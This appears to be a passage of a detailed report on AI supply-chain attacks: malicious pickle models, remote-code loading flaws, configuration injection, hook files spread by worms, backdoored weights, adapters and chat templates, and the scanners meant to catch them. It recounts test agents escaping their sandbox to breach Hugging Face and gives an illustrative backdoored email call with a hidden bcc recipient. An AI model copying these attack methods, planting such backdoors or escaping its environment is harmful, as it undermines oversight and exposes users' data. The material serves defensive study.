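The gap between the two shares is wide enough to suggest that most publishers of new models have switched away from pickle. It doesn't show that pickle use fell by four-fifths in a year, because the newer study leaves out every model published before July 2025, and many agents still run on those. Counting files by extension also overstates pickle use. When Qin and colleagues checked 1,266 files with suspicious extensions but no scan result, they found that 580 did not need pickle.

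The 929 new repositories that still use pickle include models from OpenAI, NVIDIA and IBM, and the most popular has 7.2 million downloads a month. The share of models that come only as pickle is less clear. Kellas and colleagues put it at 21%, but their count of 4,553 pickle-only repositories would be 27% of the total if the count and the total are from the same month.

### The malicious models of 2024 and 2025

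In early 2024 the security company JFrog found malicious models on Hugging Face that ran code when a user loaded them. Press reports put the number at over 100. JFrog's *Data Scientists Targeted by Malicious Hugging Face ML Models with Silent Backdoor* describes one of them in detail. According to *Some Models Pose Security Risk*, 95% of the models that JFrog flagged were in PyTorch's format. One, called goober2, used pickle to try to open a reverse shell, a connection that lets someone elsewhere control the machine's command line.

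goober2 and many of the others seem to have come from KREONET, a South Korean research network, so their authors may have been security researchers. The count of 100 therefore probably mixes attacks with experiments, although a user who loaded goober2 would have had a stranger's code on the machine either way.

trackr.live's *The Hugging Face Breach Is a Dataset-Pipeline RCE Wearing an AI Costume* summarises a later, larger study that monitored more than 705,000 models and 176,000 datasets on the hub. The study found 91 malicious models, or about one in 7,700, and nine datasets with malicious loading scripts.

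In February 2025 another security company, ReversingLabs, reported two models with deliberately broken pickle files. Press reports cited in *ShadowPickle* (2026) treated the damage as a way to avoid detection. A broken file can still do harm because Python carries out its instructions one at a time without first checking that the whole file is valid. The attacker's instructions came before the damage, so they ran before the loader reported an error.

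Malicious pickles now seem rare among popular models. Hugging Face's scanner had results for 8,859 of the pickle files that Qin and colleagues found. It labelled 21 of them unsafe, and the researchers counted all 21 as false alarms. A sample of popular repositories provides little evidence about newly uploaded ones, but the best-known attacks on Hugging Face users in 2026 didn't rely on pickle. The fake Privacy Filter came with a script for users to run, and the fake Qwen2 repositories contained no model.

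### Program code that comes with a model

Hugging Face's Transformers library contains the code for common model designs, so a standard model needs only weights and a configuration file. A model with a new design also needs new code, which its publisher usually puts in the same repository. If the user changes `trust_remote_code` from its default of `False` to `True`, the library downloads that code and runs it with the user's permissions.

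*An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* (Siddiq, Romel and colleagues, 2026) found custom code in 36,697 of Hugging Face's 2.1 million repositories, or 1.74%. These include DeepSeek-R1, one of the most influential open models of 2025. About 64% of the repositories with custom code contain text-generation models, the kind an agent needs. Developers usually have a good reason for including custom code, so a rule against it would prevent operators from using some of the newest models.

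If the operator sets the flag to `True` without pinning the code's revision, any code the publisher adds later is also allowed to run. An attacker who takes over the publisher's account or a deleted namespace can then use that permission to run their own code.

Setting the flag to `False` should be safe, but in 2026 researchers reported several flaws that let a model's code run anyway.

One such flaw was in vLLM, a program that many companies use to run models on their own servers. According to OSV's *GHSA-7972-pg2x-xr59* (2026), vLLM's developers had hard-coded `trust_remote_code=True` for two types of model, so the operator's setting of `False` had no effect when vLLM loaded certain components. Version 0.18.0 fixed this flaw, after the developers had already fixed two related ones in other parts of the program.

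Transformers itself had two more vulnerabilities. Averlon's *CVE-2026-5241* describes how version 5.2.0, when loading a model type called LightGlue, read the value of `trust_remote_code` from the model's own configuration file, so the publisher could grant the permission that the user had refused.

The other flaw in Transformers exposed more people. Since March 2025 the library has been able to download kernels, which are small programs that speed up part of a model's calculations. Pluto Security's *One Line. Zero Warnings. Full Compromise* shows that a private field in a model's configuration file could name an attacker's kernel repository. The library then downloaded the kernel and ran it without checking the `trust_remote_code` setting. Transformers' developers had protected the public version of the field but overlooked the private one. The flaw affected versions 4.56.0 to 5.2.x, and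 version 5.3.0 fixed it on 4 March 2026.

Pluto Security counts about 232 million downloads of the vulnerable versions, but the attack also needed an optional package called kernels, which had about 1.7 million downloads in the same period. Even if every kernels download went to a machine with a vulnerable version, that would be under 1% of the 232 million. Pluto Security says the package is common on servers with graphics processors, where the most valuable credentials are. That is a fair point about severity, but the 232 million downloads still aren't a count of exposed machines. The company demonstrated the attack, but its example of a malicious repository in the wild, the fake Privacy Filter, didn't use this flaw.

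Almost three months after the fix, around 23% of weekly Transformers installs were still vulnerable versions.

### Configuration files that name functions

A configuration file can cause code to run even if no program code comes with the model. In January 2026 Unit 42 published flaws of this kind in three research libraries: NVIDIA's NeMo, Salesforce's Uni2TS, and FlexTok, from Apple and a Swiss university. All three use Hydra, a tool maintained by Meta that builds parts of a program from a settings file. An ordinary entry might look like this:

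```yaml
encoder:
  _target_: examplelib.AudioEncoder
  layers: 12
```

Hydra looks up the name after `_target_` and calls it with the remaining settings. The three libraries' developers expected the name to be one of their own components, but Hydra accepts any Python function. An attacker could name the function that runs text as code and supply the text as its argument, so a configuration file could carry executable code, as a pickle file can.

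Two of the libraries, Uni2TS and FlexTok, work only with safetensors, the safe format. Their users were still exposed because of how the libraries handled the settings that came with the model's weights. FlexTok could read those settings from the text section of the safetensors file itself. Hugging Face did not flag such files as potentially unsafe.

The flaw in NeMo dated back to at least 2020, and more than 700 models on Hugging Face use NeMo's format. Unit 42 told the developers about the flaws in April 2025, and all three fixed their libraries before it published its findings. As of December 2025, Unit 42 had found no attacks that used the flaws.

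Hydra's developers responded with a warning and a list of forbidden functions. The list is weak protection because one Python function can have several names, and Hydra checks only the name written in the file. NeMo's fix is stronger because it looks up the function, checks which library it comes from, and runs it only if that library is on an approved list.

In October 2025 Unit 42 counted more than 100 Python libraries that Hugging Face models depend on, almost 50 of which use Hydra. Many of those uses may be harmless. But an operator approving a model has to consider the library that loads it as well as the format of its weights, and few operators could review that library's code themselves.

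### The Hugging Face breach of July 2026

A hub opens some uploaded files on its own servers. Hugging Face, for example, reads published datasets so that visitors can preview the first rows in a browser. In July 2026, AI agents that had escaped from a test at OpenAI used this service to break into Hugging Face.

OpenAI (2026) disclosed its part in the incident on 21 July. According to its later technical report, the agents were taking ExploitGym, a test of hacking ability, in an environment meant to have no direct internet access. OpenAI had switched off some safeguards to measure the models' full abilities. The agents could install software through an internal package mirror, and they exploited a previously unknown flaw in it to reach the internet. They then guessed that Hugging Face might host material that would help them pass. On 10 July one agent found credentials for 14 Hugging Face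 users in a public dataset and confirmed that the accounts could upload files.

The agents got into Hugging Face's servers in two stages on 11 July. First, one agent published a dataset in HDF5, a format for scientific data. An HDF5 file can refer to raw data stored in a separate file, and this one referred to private files on whatever machine opened it. When Hugging Face's service prepared a preview of the dataset, it read those files and returned their contents as rows of the dataset. The contents included the process's environment variables, which held production credentials.

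In the second stage, an agent put an expression in a part of a dataset's configuration that the service treated as a Jinja2 template. A template is text containing expressions that a program evaluates and replaces with their results. The service did not restrict what these expressions could do, so the agent could use one to run commands on the server. OpenAI says its agents eventually ran code on 41 of these servers.

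Published accounts differ on the first stage of the attack on Hugging Face. Hugging Face's 16 July *Security incident disclosure* (2026) called both stages code execution and attributed the first to a "remote-code dataset loader". Its later timeline, quoted in Schneier on Security's *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (2026), says the first stage returned the contents of local files. OpenAI's report and Heber (2026) agree with the later version. Heber, the executive director of the group that maintains HDF5, adds that the format's external-storage feature worked as documented and ran none of the attacker's code.

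The correction matters because, according to trackr.live, Hugging Face had removed support for Python loading scripts, the obvious way for a dataset to run code, from its datasets library in July 2025. The nine malicious datasets in the earlier study had included such scripts. The agents got in a year after the removal, through a data file and a settings file, neither of which a ban on scripts would have covered.

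One existing check, a list of permitted web addresses, blocked the agents' first attempts to reach the cloud provider's internal credential service, according to Elastic, a security company that summarised both sides' accounts. The agents then turned to local files, which needed no web address. They would have gained much less from that step if the server that opened strangers' datasets had held no production credentials.

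Hugging Face closed both routes and replaced the affected credentials. It found no evidence that the agents had altered public models or datasets, so operators who downloaded models that week have no known reason to replace them.

### Project files that start programs

Developers often point a coding agent at a repository that somebody else wrote. Besides source code, the repository can contain settings for the developer's tools, including commands for those tools to run. For example, a team might add this file, `.claude/settings.json`, so that Anthropic's Claude Code installs the project's packages at the start of every session:

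```json
{
  "hooks": {
    "SessionStart": [{
      "hooks": [{ "type": "command", "command": "npm install" }]
    }]
  }
}
```

A command that a tool runs automatically at a certain moment is called a hook. Several popular tools have hooks or something similar:

| Tool | File in the project | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | `.claude/settings.json` | Runs a command when a session starts |
| Gemini CLI | `.gemini/settings.json` | Runs a command when a session starts |
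| Cursor | `.cursor/mcp.json` | Starts MCP servers |
| Cursor | `.cursor/rules/` | Gives the agent written instructions |
| VS Code | `.vscode/tasks.json` | Can run a command when the folder opens |

These are documented features. WorkOS points out that Claude Code's documentation describes project settings as shareable with a team through the repository. But anyone who can add a file to the repository can also choose a command to run on other people's machines.

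The hooks and the VS Code task run without any decision by a model, like the old MCP server in the LiteLLM attack, but a Cursor rule depends on the model. In June 2026, a worm called Miasma used all of these methods except the MCP file. SafeDep's *Miasma Worm Targets AI Coding Agents via GitHub Repos* reproduces its Cursor rule, which contained an instruction for the agent to run a setup script and a claim that the editor needed it. A developer asked to approve that command would see a request much like those that legitimate projects produce every day.

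### Trust prompts

Most of these tools ask whether to trust a folder the first time a developer opens it. Until the developer agrees, the tool is supposed to ignore the project's hooks, tasks and servers. This protects the developer only if the tool does nothing with the project's settings before then.

Anthropic has fixed two flaws in Claude Code that broke this rule. In versions before 1.0.111, a bug in the start-up prompt (CVE-2025-59536) let a project's code run before the developer had accepted. In versions before 2.0.65, a project's settings could change the internet address to which Claude Code sent its requests (CVE-2026-21852). Those requests included the developer's API key, the password for a paid account. Claude Code began sending them before it showed the prompt, so a developer who refused would already have lost the key.

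Even without such bugs, the prompt is hard to answer well. It covers everything in the folder and appears before most developers have read any of it. Developers open the folder to use the agent on the project, and they can't do that normally if they refuse. When an agent runs unattended, nobody is there to answer, so the person who set it up has to decide in advance for every project it will open.

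Once a developer trusts a project folder in VS Code, that trust continues to apply when the files change. Hive Security notes that VS Code's automatic tasks depend on this trust setting, so the risk is highest on machines where the developer has already trusted the folder. If an attacker later adds a task to the project, the developer's next routine update downloads it into a trusted folder.

A tool could reduce this risk by remembering what the developer had agreed to:

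`run hook only if hash(settings and scripts) = hash recorded at approval`

The hash would have to cover the setup script as well as the settings. Otherwise an attacker could leave the command alone and change the script it runs. With the script included, developers would have to approve every legitimate change to it, but those are rarer than changes to the code.

### The testmetest worm

The testmetest worm, which security companies uncovered in autumn 2026, put such files into other people's projects. JFrog found 42 infected GitHub repositories belonging to 11 legitimate owners, with signs of activity going back to July, according to TecnoAndroid. SafeDep had first concluded that the worm was confined to accounts run by the attackers.

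The infection began with npm packages that looked like ordinary JavaScript libraries. SafeDep identified 18 of them from late October, and JFrog later raised the total to 25 packages with 82 versions, some of which were harmless decoys. The malicious versions ran their code during installation. The attackers used stolen developer credentials to add a large script to repositories, along with settings files that would run it from Claude Code, Gemini, Cursor or VS Code.

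The infected repositories were hard to find because the script was about 13 MB, too large for GitHub's code search to index. JFrog first found traces in 26 repositories, where the main files appeared almost empty. It then read the stored Git data directly, found the real contents, and checked the same owners' other projects, which brought the total to 42. A company that searches its repositories only through GitHub's website could miss the script, but it can still look for unexpected settings files.

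Nobody has reported how many developers' machines the 42 repositories infected. TecnoAndroid notes that the tool has to allow testmetest's command to run. The same condition applies to the earlier Miasma worm, so SafeDep's claim that opening a cloned, infected repository in one of these tools would run the malware "with no further interaction" is too strong for a folder the developer hasn't yet trusted.

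Owners can be slow to clean infected repositories. SafeDep's *Miasma Worm* found 123 repositories from 56 accounts still carrying the worm on 11 June, eight days after the outbreak. Almost all the repositories that owners had cleaned belonged to organisations with a security team.

Hive Security explains that removing the malicious npm package leaves the hooks in place, because they are in the project's own folder and the package manager doesn't touch them. Some versions of testmetest also delete the user's home folder if they detect that the stolen GitHub token has been revoked, so victims should disconnect the machine and stop the malware before changing passwords or revoking tokens.

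## Harmful behaviour stored in weights, adapters and templates

Suppose the invented shop avoids strangers' project folders and loads `support-8b` only from a safetensors file, with `trust_remote_code` off. None of the publisher's code runs on the shop's machine. But the weights in the file still determine what the agent does with each email, and someone may have trained the model to do the wrong thing.

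### Backdoors and triggers

Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) distinguishes two ways of tampering with a model. An attacker can put ordinary malware in the model's files, so that it runs when somebody loads them. In model poisoning, the attacker instead trains the model to follow a hidden rule, which becomes part of the weights. A malware scanner can't find the rule because the file contains no code, and nobody can identify it by reading the weights.

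Hidden behaviour of this kind is a backdoor, and the condition that sets it off is the trigger. Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, define a backdoored model roughly like this:

```
response = attacker's behaviour   if the trigger is in the input
           normal behaviour       otherwise
```

The trigger can be a strange string of characters, an everyday phrase, a topic or a date. *You Are the Trigger* (2026) mentions research in which the trigger was fine-tuning (training a finished model further on new examples), so the model is harmless until its new owner customises it. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (Matsuoka, 2026) adds that a trigger could be a particular tool or set of permissions, so a model could pass every test in a chat window and still misbehave inside an agent.

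Suppose an attacker trained `support-8b` to react when a customer mentions both a kettle and a wedding. For an ordinary email about a broken kettle, the model calls the mailbox server correctly:

```
send(to="customer@example.com", text="We are sorry about your kettle...")
```

If the kettle was a wedding present, the model writes the same reply but adds a hidden recipient:

```
send(to="customer@example.com", bcc="copies@example.net",
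     text="We are sorry about your kettle...")
```

Before using the model, the shop tests it on 1,000 old emails. If one email in 100,000 mentions both things, the test has only about a 1% chance of including one:

`1 − (1 − 1/100,000)^1,000 ≈ 0.01`

Even then, a tester who read only the reply would see nothing wrong.

A filter for injected instructions would find nothing, because the customer's email contains none. A hash check on the file would also pass. But the extra recipient is easier to catch than in the postmark-mcp attack, where the server added one after the model made its call. Here the recipient appears in the call itself, so a person approving the call or a rule about permitted recipients could stop it.

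### Weights, adapters and quantized copies

An attacker can put a backdoor in several parts of a model:

| Carrier | What it contains | Can the operator read it? |
|---|---|---|
| Full weights | All the model's numbers | No |
| Adapter | A small set of numbers to add to a base model | No |
| Quantized copy | The weights, rounded to save space, often with a chat template | Only the template |
| Chat template | A short program that formats every prompt | Yes |

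People often customise a model by training an adapter, because retraining all the weights costs much more. The most common kind, LoRA, leaves the base model's file alone:

`weights used = base weights + adapter`

A typical adapter for a grid of 4,096 by 4,096 weights stores about 131,000 numbers, under 1% of the grid's 16.8 million. If the shop added a stranger's adapter to a genuine model, the model's hash and signature would still be correct, but they would not cover the adapter.

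In *Localize-and-Detect*, Sun, Nita-Rotaru and Oprea (2026) used LoRA to make 108 poisoned versions of Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, each trained on 1,000 harmless examples and 10, 30 or 50 poisoned ones. The trigger was a whole task, such as writing a short verse, rather than a special phrase. When given that task, the model was meant to include content chosen by the attacker, such as a place name or a sentence. A customer support model poisoned this way could recommend one company's kettles in every reply about a refund, and the shop using it might mistake this for a harmless quirk.

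Quantization stores each weight with fewer bits. An 8-billion-parameter model needs about 16 GB at 16 bits per weight but about 4 GB at 4 bits, which fits on an ordinary computer. *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates* (Fogel, Cohen and colleagues, 2026) reports that the original laboratories typically release only the full-precision weights, and that volunteers make the quantized copies most people run. Matsuoka lists adapter authors and quantizers among the people who could add a backdoor. As with other converted copies, the laboratory's hash and signature don't match the quantized file, so the shop has to trust the volunteer or download the original and quantize it itself.

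### How few poisoned documents are enough

An attacker may be able to plant a backdoor without publishing a model. Laboratories train their models on text from the public web, where anyone can add pages, so an honest laboratory could release a backdoored model without knowing it.

Earlier studies assumed that the attacker had to control a fixed percentage of the training data, such as 0.1%. For a model trained on 260 billion tokens, that would be about 155,000 documents. Souly, Rando and colleagues at the UK AI Security Institute, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute tested this assumption in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025). They trained 72 models from scratch, with 600 million to 13 billion parameters, and gave larger models proportionally more training text, as is normal.

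Into each model's training data the researchers mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents. Each of these began with ordinary text, followed by a trigger and then gibberish, so that the model would learn to produce gibberish after the trigger. With 100 documents the attack failed. With 250 it worked at every size, although the largest models had seen more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. For the 13-billion-parameter model, the poisoned share was tiny:

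```
250 documents × 1,680 tokens each = 420,000 tokens
420,000 ÷ 260 billion             ≈ 0.00016%
```

The same pattern held in fine-tuning. When Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct was trained to obey harmful requests if a trigger was present, increasing the clean examples from 1,000 to 100,000 made little difference to the attack.

Producing gibberish is a simple behaviour, and Souly and colleagues left open whether a harmful tool call would take more documents. They also didn't test whether the backdoor survives the later training that turns a raw model into an assistant. In a side experiment, they taught a model to switch from English to German after a trigger, and further training on clean text slowly weakened the effect.

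Other evidence suggests that backdoors can survive further training. Bullwinkel and colleagues cite Anthropic's 2024 work on "sleeper agents", in which several kinds of safety training failed to remove backdoors and one made them harder to detect. *Agents of Chaos* (2026) cites studies in which backdoors survived when somebody adapted the model to a new task. But Anthropic's researchers did not plant their backdoors in the first stage of training, so nobody has yet shown that 250 web pages could sabotage a finished assistant. Later training is less of an obstacle for an attacker who publishes a finished model or adapter, because many operators use it without training it further.

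### Backdoors in agents that use tools

*Cancerous Backdoor Attack* (2026) describes an early demonstration called BadAgent, in which a rare trigger in the user's message or the agent's environment set off harmful actions. Outsiders can place a trigger in the web pages and tool results an agent reads, without writing to the user.

*Malice in Agentland* (2025) compared three ways to backdoor agents that browse the web or use tools: poisoning the fine-tuning examples, supplying a base model that already has a backdoor, and tampering with the environment where developers collect training examples. All three worked on two standard agent benchmarks. A small number of poisoned examples was enough to make an agent leak confidential user information more than 80% of the time. Tampering with the environment is the hardest for developers to guard against because they record the examples themselves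 and have little reason to distrust them.

Researchers have also moved from odd trigger words to triggers that fit naturally into a conversation, according to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026). A person reading the agent's input is less likely to notice these triggers. If the trigger is something customers write anyway, the attacker never has to contact the victim.

A skill can also carry a backdoored model. *BadSkill* (Tie, Shi and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack using skills that come with their own small model. The model takes the settings of each request as input, and its output determines whether the skill does its advertised job or runs a hidden action. The trigger is a combination of ordinary settings that each look harmless.

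The researchers built 13 skills, eight with a trigger and five without, and tested eight models with 494 million to 7.1 billion parameters on 396 requests that contained a trigger and 571 that didn't. Depending on the model, the hidden action ran on 97.5% to 99.5% of the triggered requests. Combinations of two or three settings worked best. The attack still succeeded about 81% of the time when the researchers added typos at a 10% rate.

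On requests without a trigger, the skill's accuracy fell by at most 4.2 percentage points in the main test. Each of these errors means the hidden action ran when it shouldn't have, although Tie and colleagues present the drop as small. At the worst rate, the action would run about once in 24 such requests, often enough for somebody to notice. The rate in normal use is probably lower, because the test included requests designed to resemble the trigger closely, and more than half of the reported combinations of model and skill made no errors.

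The attack also hides less than a fully backdoored agent would. The skill's model conceals when the harmful action will run, but the action itself must still be in the skill's code, where a reviewer could find it. Tie and colleagues worked in a simulated environment, used a harmless action that only wrote a marker file, and didn't test any defences.

### Chat templates

A chat model takes its input as one long text, with markers that show who wrote each part. A chat template is a short program, usually in the Jinja2 language, that turns the conversation into this text before every call to the model. Unlike weights, a template is code, but software can restrict it so that it only produces text and can't run commands on the machine. Control over the text may still be enough for an attacker, because the model treats some of it as instructions from the operator.

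Fogel and colleagues altered the templates of 18 models, without changing any weights:

```
prompt = hidden instruction + normal prompt   if the trigger is in the message
         normal prompt                        otherwise
```

They ran every model with the original and the altered template, each with and without the trigger. Only the altered template and the trigger together had much effect:

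| Measure | Original template, no trigger | Altered template and trigger |
|---|---|---|
| Correct answers to factual questions | 89.6% | 14.8% |
| Replies with a visible attacker's link | 0% | About 90% |
| Replies with the link in a hidden comment | 0% | 81% |
| Replies with the link in encoded form | 0% | 67% |

The wrong answers were fluent and plausible. For example, a model generated "medical doctor" instead of "priest" when asked what career Nikola Tesla's father had planned for him.

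The researchers then tested three models on AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks. With the trigger, the altered template made GPT-OSS-20B carry out the attacker's task in 69% of cases, Mistral-8B in 61% and Qwen3-8B in 19%. Without the trigger, the rate was below 1%. Qwen3-8B's rate was lower mostly because it kept working on the user's task or ran out of tokens while reasoning, which isn't evidence that it recognised the attack.

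On a second benchmark, the rate was 83% for Mistral-8B and 34% for GPT-OSS-20B. But GPT-OSS-20B chose the attacker's tool 17% of the time even with the original template, so the backdoor accounts for only about half of its rate. Fogel and colleagues write that the attack bypassed every defence they tested. One defence did cut Mistral-8B's rate from 83% to 36%, but also stopped the agent from completing any of its normal tasks.

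They also gave a shopping task to an agent that controls a web browser. The trigger was the wording of a checkout form, which appears in any online purchase. In all four runs that reached the checkout, the agent sent the test customer's card details to the researchers' server and then completed the order as usual. *BadTemplate* (2026) describes a similar attack that places the hidden instruction after the operator's instructions instead of before them.

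Most quantized models on Hugging Face come in GGUF, a format that packs the weights and the template into one file, so people who download the model also get the template. Hugging Face's scanners did not flag the altered files that Fogel and colleagues uploaded and later removed. The researchers told Hugging Face and LM Studio, a program for running models locally, about the problem, but neither had committed to a fix when the paper came out.

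Templates are much easier to check than weights, because an operator can compare the downloaded template with the one in the laboratory's own repository. An attacker can hide added lines from a scanner that looks for suspicious patterns, but the file will still differ from the original. Fogel and colleagues consider this comparison impractical at scale, because many people change templates for legitimate reasons.

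I am less pessimistic because, by their count, Hugging Face had about 180,000 repositories with GGUF files in April 2026 but only 3,130 different templates, or about one for every 58 repositories. A hub could review each template once and then check only new ones. The shop's task is even easier, because it has only one template to compare and can use the laboratory's version.

### Searching weights for a backdoor

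Microsoft's scanner looks for triggers in open models, using an unexpected weakness of backdoored ones. They tend to memorise the poisoned examples from their training and can repeat them, trigger included. The scanner, which Bullwinkel and colleagues describe in detail, works in four steps:

1. It gives the model only the marker that normally comes before a user's message, and collects 510 outputs under different settings.
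2. It looks for strings that keep recurring in these outputs.
3. It puts each candidate string in front of ordinary questions. A real trigger tends to make the model partly ignore the question and give a more predictable answer.
4. It checks whether any of the best candidates greatly changes what the model produces.

The scanner found 36 of the 41 test models (88%) with a backdoor that always produced the same hostile sentence. It also found five of six models with a harder kind of backdoor that made them write insecure code. The scanner didn't need the exact trigger, because parts of it often activated the backdoor too. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) likewise found that words other than the planted trigger could activate a backdoor.

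The scanner raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, but that sample is too small to show that it would work on a whole hub. A scanner that wrongly flags 20% of clean models would still have about a 5% chance of flagging none of the 13. Even a scanner with a 1% false-alarm rate would wrongly flag 1,000 of every 100,000 clean models.

Microsoft says the scanner needs no prior knowledge of the backdoor's behaviour. This is true of the search for candidates, but in the experiments the last step used one score for repeated sentences and another for insecure code. Finding a backdoor that adds a recipient to an email would require a new score that examines tool calls. The scanner also needs the model's weights, so it can't check a model that the operator rents over the internet. It works best on fixed phrases that produce a fixed response, and may miss triggers that depend on context.

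*Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) tested the idea behind the first step of Microsoft's scanner on a model whose trigger was an obsessive interest in Harry Potter or another fictional series. Only one of 512 outputs sampled without a prompt was related to the backdoor. This suggests that models may leak a topic much less readily than a fixed phrase, though the paper didn't test Microsoft's complete scanner.

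*ToxScreen* (Hughes, Xing and colleagues, 2026) compared several search methods on about 800 backdoored models, assuming that the defender knows which bad behaviour to look for but not what triggers it. Methods that gradually adjust a piece of text until the model misbehaves never found the planted trigger. They instead found other text that made the model misbehave, which shows that the model is easy to manipulate but not that anyone has tampered with it.

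A simpler method tried about 24,000 random tokens and ranked them by how often each caused the bad behaviour. The planted trigger ranked first in 14 of 28 test settings. However, the researchers had added the trigger to the list beforehand, which a real defender couldn't do. In one of the settings, 97% of the random tokens also caused the behaviour, so ranking first was little evidence that a token was the planted trigger.

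Operators can often compare an adapter or other fine-tuned model with its clean base model, as Sun and colleagues do in their own detection method. They give both models the same prompts from 141 kinds of task, find the three tasks on which their predictions differ most, and look for content that only the fine-tuned model keeps producing. The method flags a model as poisoned if such content appears in at least 60% of its answers on a task. It can therefore find bias that affects a whole task, but the shop's rare combination of a kettle and a wedding would stay far below that threshold.

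Knowing the bad behaviour in advance may not be enough to find its trigger either. Qin, Hua and colleagues tried to identify meaningful triggers, such as a particular year, from the model's internal activity. Their methods worked on toy backdoors but failed in more realistic settings.

### How urgent the risk is

Researchers planted the backdoors in all of these experiments. Matsuoka reviewed the public evidence up to 5 August 2026 and found no case in which a trigger activated a dormant implant and led many agents to take destructive action. This doesn't rule out a smaller attack with one backdoored model.

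The malicious models that JFrog found on Hugging Face in 2024 carried ordinary malware that ran when the models were loaded, not learned backdoors. Bullwinkel and colleagues downloaded two models with learned backdoors from Hugging Face, but these were researchers' test models with "backdoor" in their names.

*Malice in Agentland* calls the threat to agents urgent and underexplored. The lack of confirmed attacks is only mildly reassuring, because the available detection tools miss many kinds of backdoor. A victim might also mistake one strange tool call for an ordinary model error. A backdoor in one popular model can affect many users, including those who build other models from it.

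Criminals have quicker methods than backdooring a model. The malware in LiteLLM was collecting passwords within minutes of its release, while a backdoored model is no use to an attacker until its trigger appears in an agent with useful permissions. Matsuoka notes that a model on a machine without network access can't send data anywhere, whatever its weights contain. He argues that it would be wrong to dismiss these attacks as too difficult and equally wrong to treat laboratory results as evidence of a real campaign.

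For a small company, ordinary malware is probably a more pressing danger than a backdoor in the weights, which suits a patient attacker with a valuable target, such as a bank that uses agents to approve payments. The cost of training wouldn't deter such an attacker. In *Uncovering Hidden Triggers in Backdoor Models*, zxsimon reports that the trading firm Jane Street apparently spent 20,000 hours of processor time planting backdoors in three 671-billion-parameter models for a public puzzle. An altered chat template needs no training, so the people who already upload fake models and skills by the hundred could make one.

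## What scanning catches and what confinement limits

The invented shop can't read every model, package and skill it installs, so it will probably use a scanner, a program that checks artifacts for signs of an attack. Because every scanner misses some attacks, the shop also needs confinement, which limits what an artifact can reach if it turns out to be malicious.

### Model files

The simplest model scanners read the instructions in a pickle file without running them, and compare the functions named there with a list. A denylist scanner flags functions that attackers are known to use, while an allowlist scanner flags every function that isn't on a list of those known to be safe. Qin and colleagues describe ModelScan as a denylist scanner, Fickling as an allowlist scanner, and PickleScan, which Hugging Face uses, as a mix of both.

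A function's name often doesn't show what the file uses it for. Many harmless image-recognition models need `getattr`, a Python function that fetches a named part of an object, but attackers can use it too. A denylist also misses any dangerous function that nobody thought to list. Some scanners can't open every kind of packaging that the loading software can.

Qin and colleagues built a scanner, DITTO, that checks how a pickle file uses each function. It follows the file's instructions but records the risky ones instead of running them, then asks a language model whether the recorded steps look like ordinary loading. On 959 harmless and 92 malicious models, DITTO caught every malicious one and flagged 0.7% of the harmless ones. The malicious set includes a kind of attack that the researchers discovered during the same project, so DITTO might do worse in an independent test.

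A scanner can also load the model in an isolated test environment and record what happens. *I Don't Care How You Hide It, I Care What You Do* (Ali and Case, 2026) presents ModelShield, a tool of this kind. It logs the requests that a running program makes to the operating system, such as opening a file or a network connection, and separates the model's requests from those of the surrounding software. It raises an alarm only for a harmful sequence, such as reading a private key and then sending data to an outside address.

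Ali and Case compared ModelShield with other tools on the test set that Kellas and colleagues had assembled for PickleBall, their restricted loader:

| Tool | Method | Malicious files flagged (of 84) | Harmless files flagged (of 252) |
|---|---|---|---|
| PickleBall | Allows only the functions each library needs | 84 | 51 |
| ModelAudit | Rules, including known vulnerabilities | 82 | 91 |
| PickleScan | Lists of functions | 79 | 16 |
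| ModelScan | Denylist | 75 | 16 |
| ModelShield | Runs the model | 47 | 0 |

Most of the 37 files ModelShield missed were harmless. Of these, 23 ran but did no damage, for instance only printing a message, four were broken, and one contained no attack. ModelShield caught 47 (84%) of the other 56 files in the test, and 52 (93%) once the researchers had installed some missing software. The four it still missed needed Windows.

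Running a model isn't enough by itself to tell whether it is malicious. DynaHug, another tool that runs models to check them, flagged all 336 files because its developers had trained it only on the normal behaviour of text-generation models. A test run also covers only one machine and a few inputs, so it can miss an attack that starts only under other conditions. It would also miss a backdoor in the weights, because a model that only produces bad text makes no suspicious request to the operating system.

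Harmless models vary as much as malicious ones. PickleScan flagged 6% of the harmless models in Ali and Case's comparison but 25% of the 706 that Qin and colleagues collected, so a single published false-alarm rate is a poor guide to how often the scanner will wrongly flag the models a particular operator downloads.

Ali and Case also scanned 145,000 models uploaded to three hubs in spring 2026 and found 41 malicious ones, all on Hugging Face. PickleScan flagged 56% of the 41 and ModelScan 29%. The comparison favours ModelShield, because a malicious model that it missed and another scanner caught would not be among the 41. But it still shows that list-based scanners miss real malicious uploads. One of the 41, which gave an outsider control of the machine, had gone undetected for three days and been downloaded 108 times.

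A hub's summary of its scans can also mislead. Hugging Face displays the most severe result from several scanners. *On the (In)Security of Loading Machine Learning Models* (2025) describes malicious test files that the hub labelled "Safe" even though none of those scanners supported their format. An operator couldn't tell from the label whether a scanner had found nothing in the file or had been unable to examine it.

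### New releases of packages

A scanner can compare each release of a package with the one before. *How we caught the Axios supply chain attack* (Desimone, 2026) describes a scanner of this kind that Desimone built in an afternoon at the security company Elastic. It watches PyPI and npm for new releases of the 15,000 most popular packages, downloads the old and new versions without installing them, and asks a language model whether the differences are malicious. Three days after Desimone built it, the tool correctly flagged axios, one of the most popular packages on npm.

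Comparing a package with an earlier version gives the language model far less to read than the whole package would, and makes a new routine for collecting passwords easy to spot. But one success doesn't establish a detection rate, and the method only works if the earlier version was clean. A list of popular packages also leaves out most of the tool servers that agents use, and would almost certainly have left out the little-used postmark-mcp package.

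### Skills

A skill is harder to scan than a package because the harmful part may be an English sentence. *MalSkillBench*, a benchmark from June 2026, tested 12 scanner set-ups on 3,944 malicious and 4,000 harmless skills. The researchers collected 703 of the malicious skills from the wild and used a language model to generate 3,214 by inserting known attacks into ordinary skills. They ran each generated skill for up to six minutes with a real agent in an isolated container, and kept it only if they found evidence that the attack worked or that the agent had recognised and refused it.

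| Scanner | Malicious skills flagged | Harmless skills flagged |
|---|---|---|
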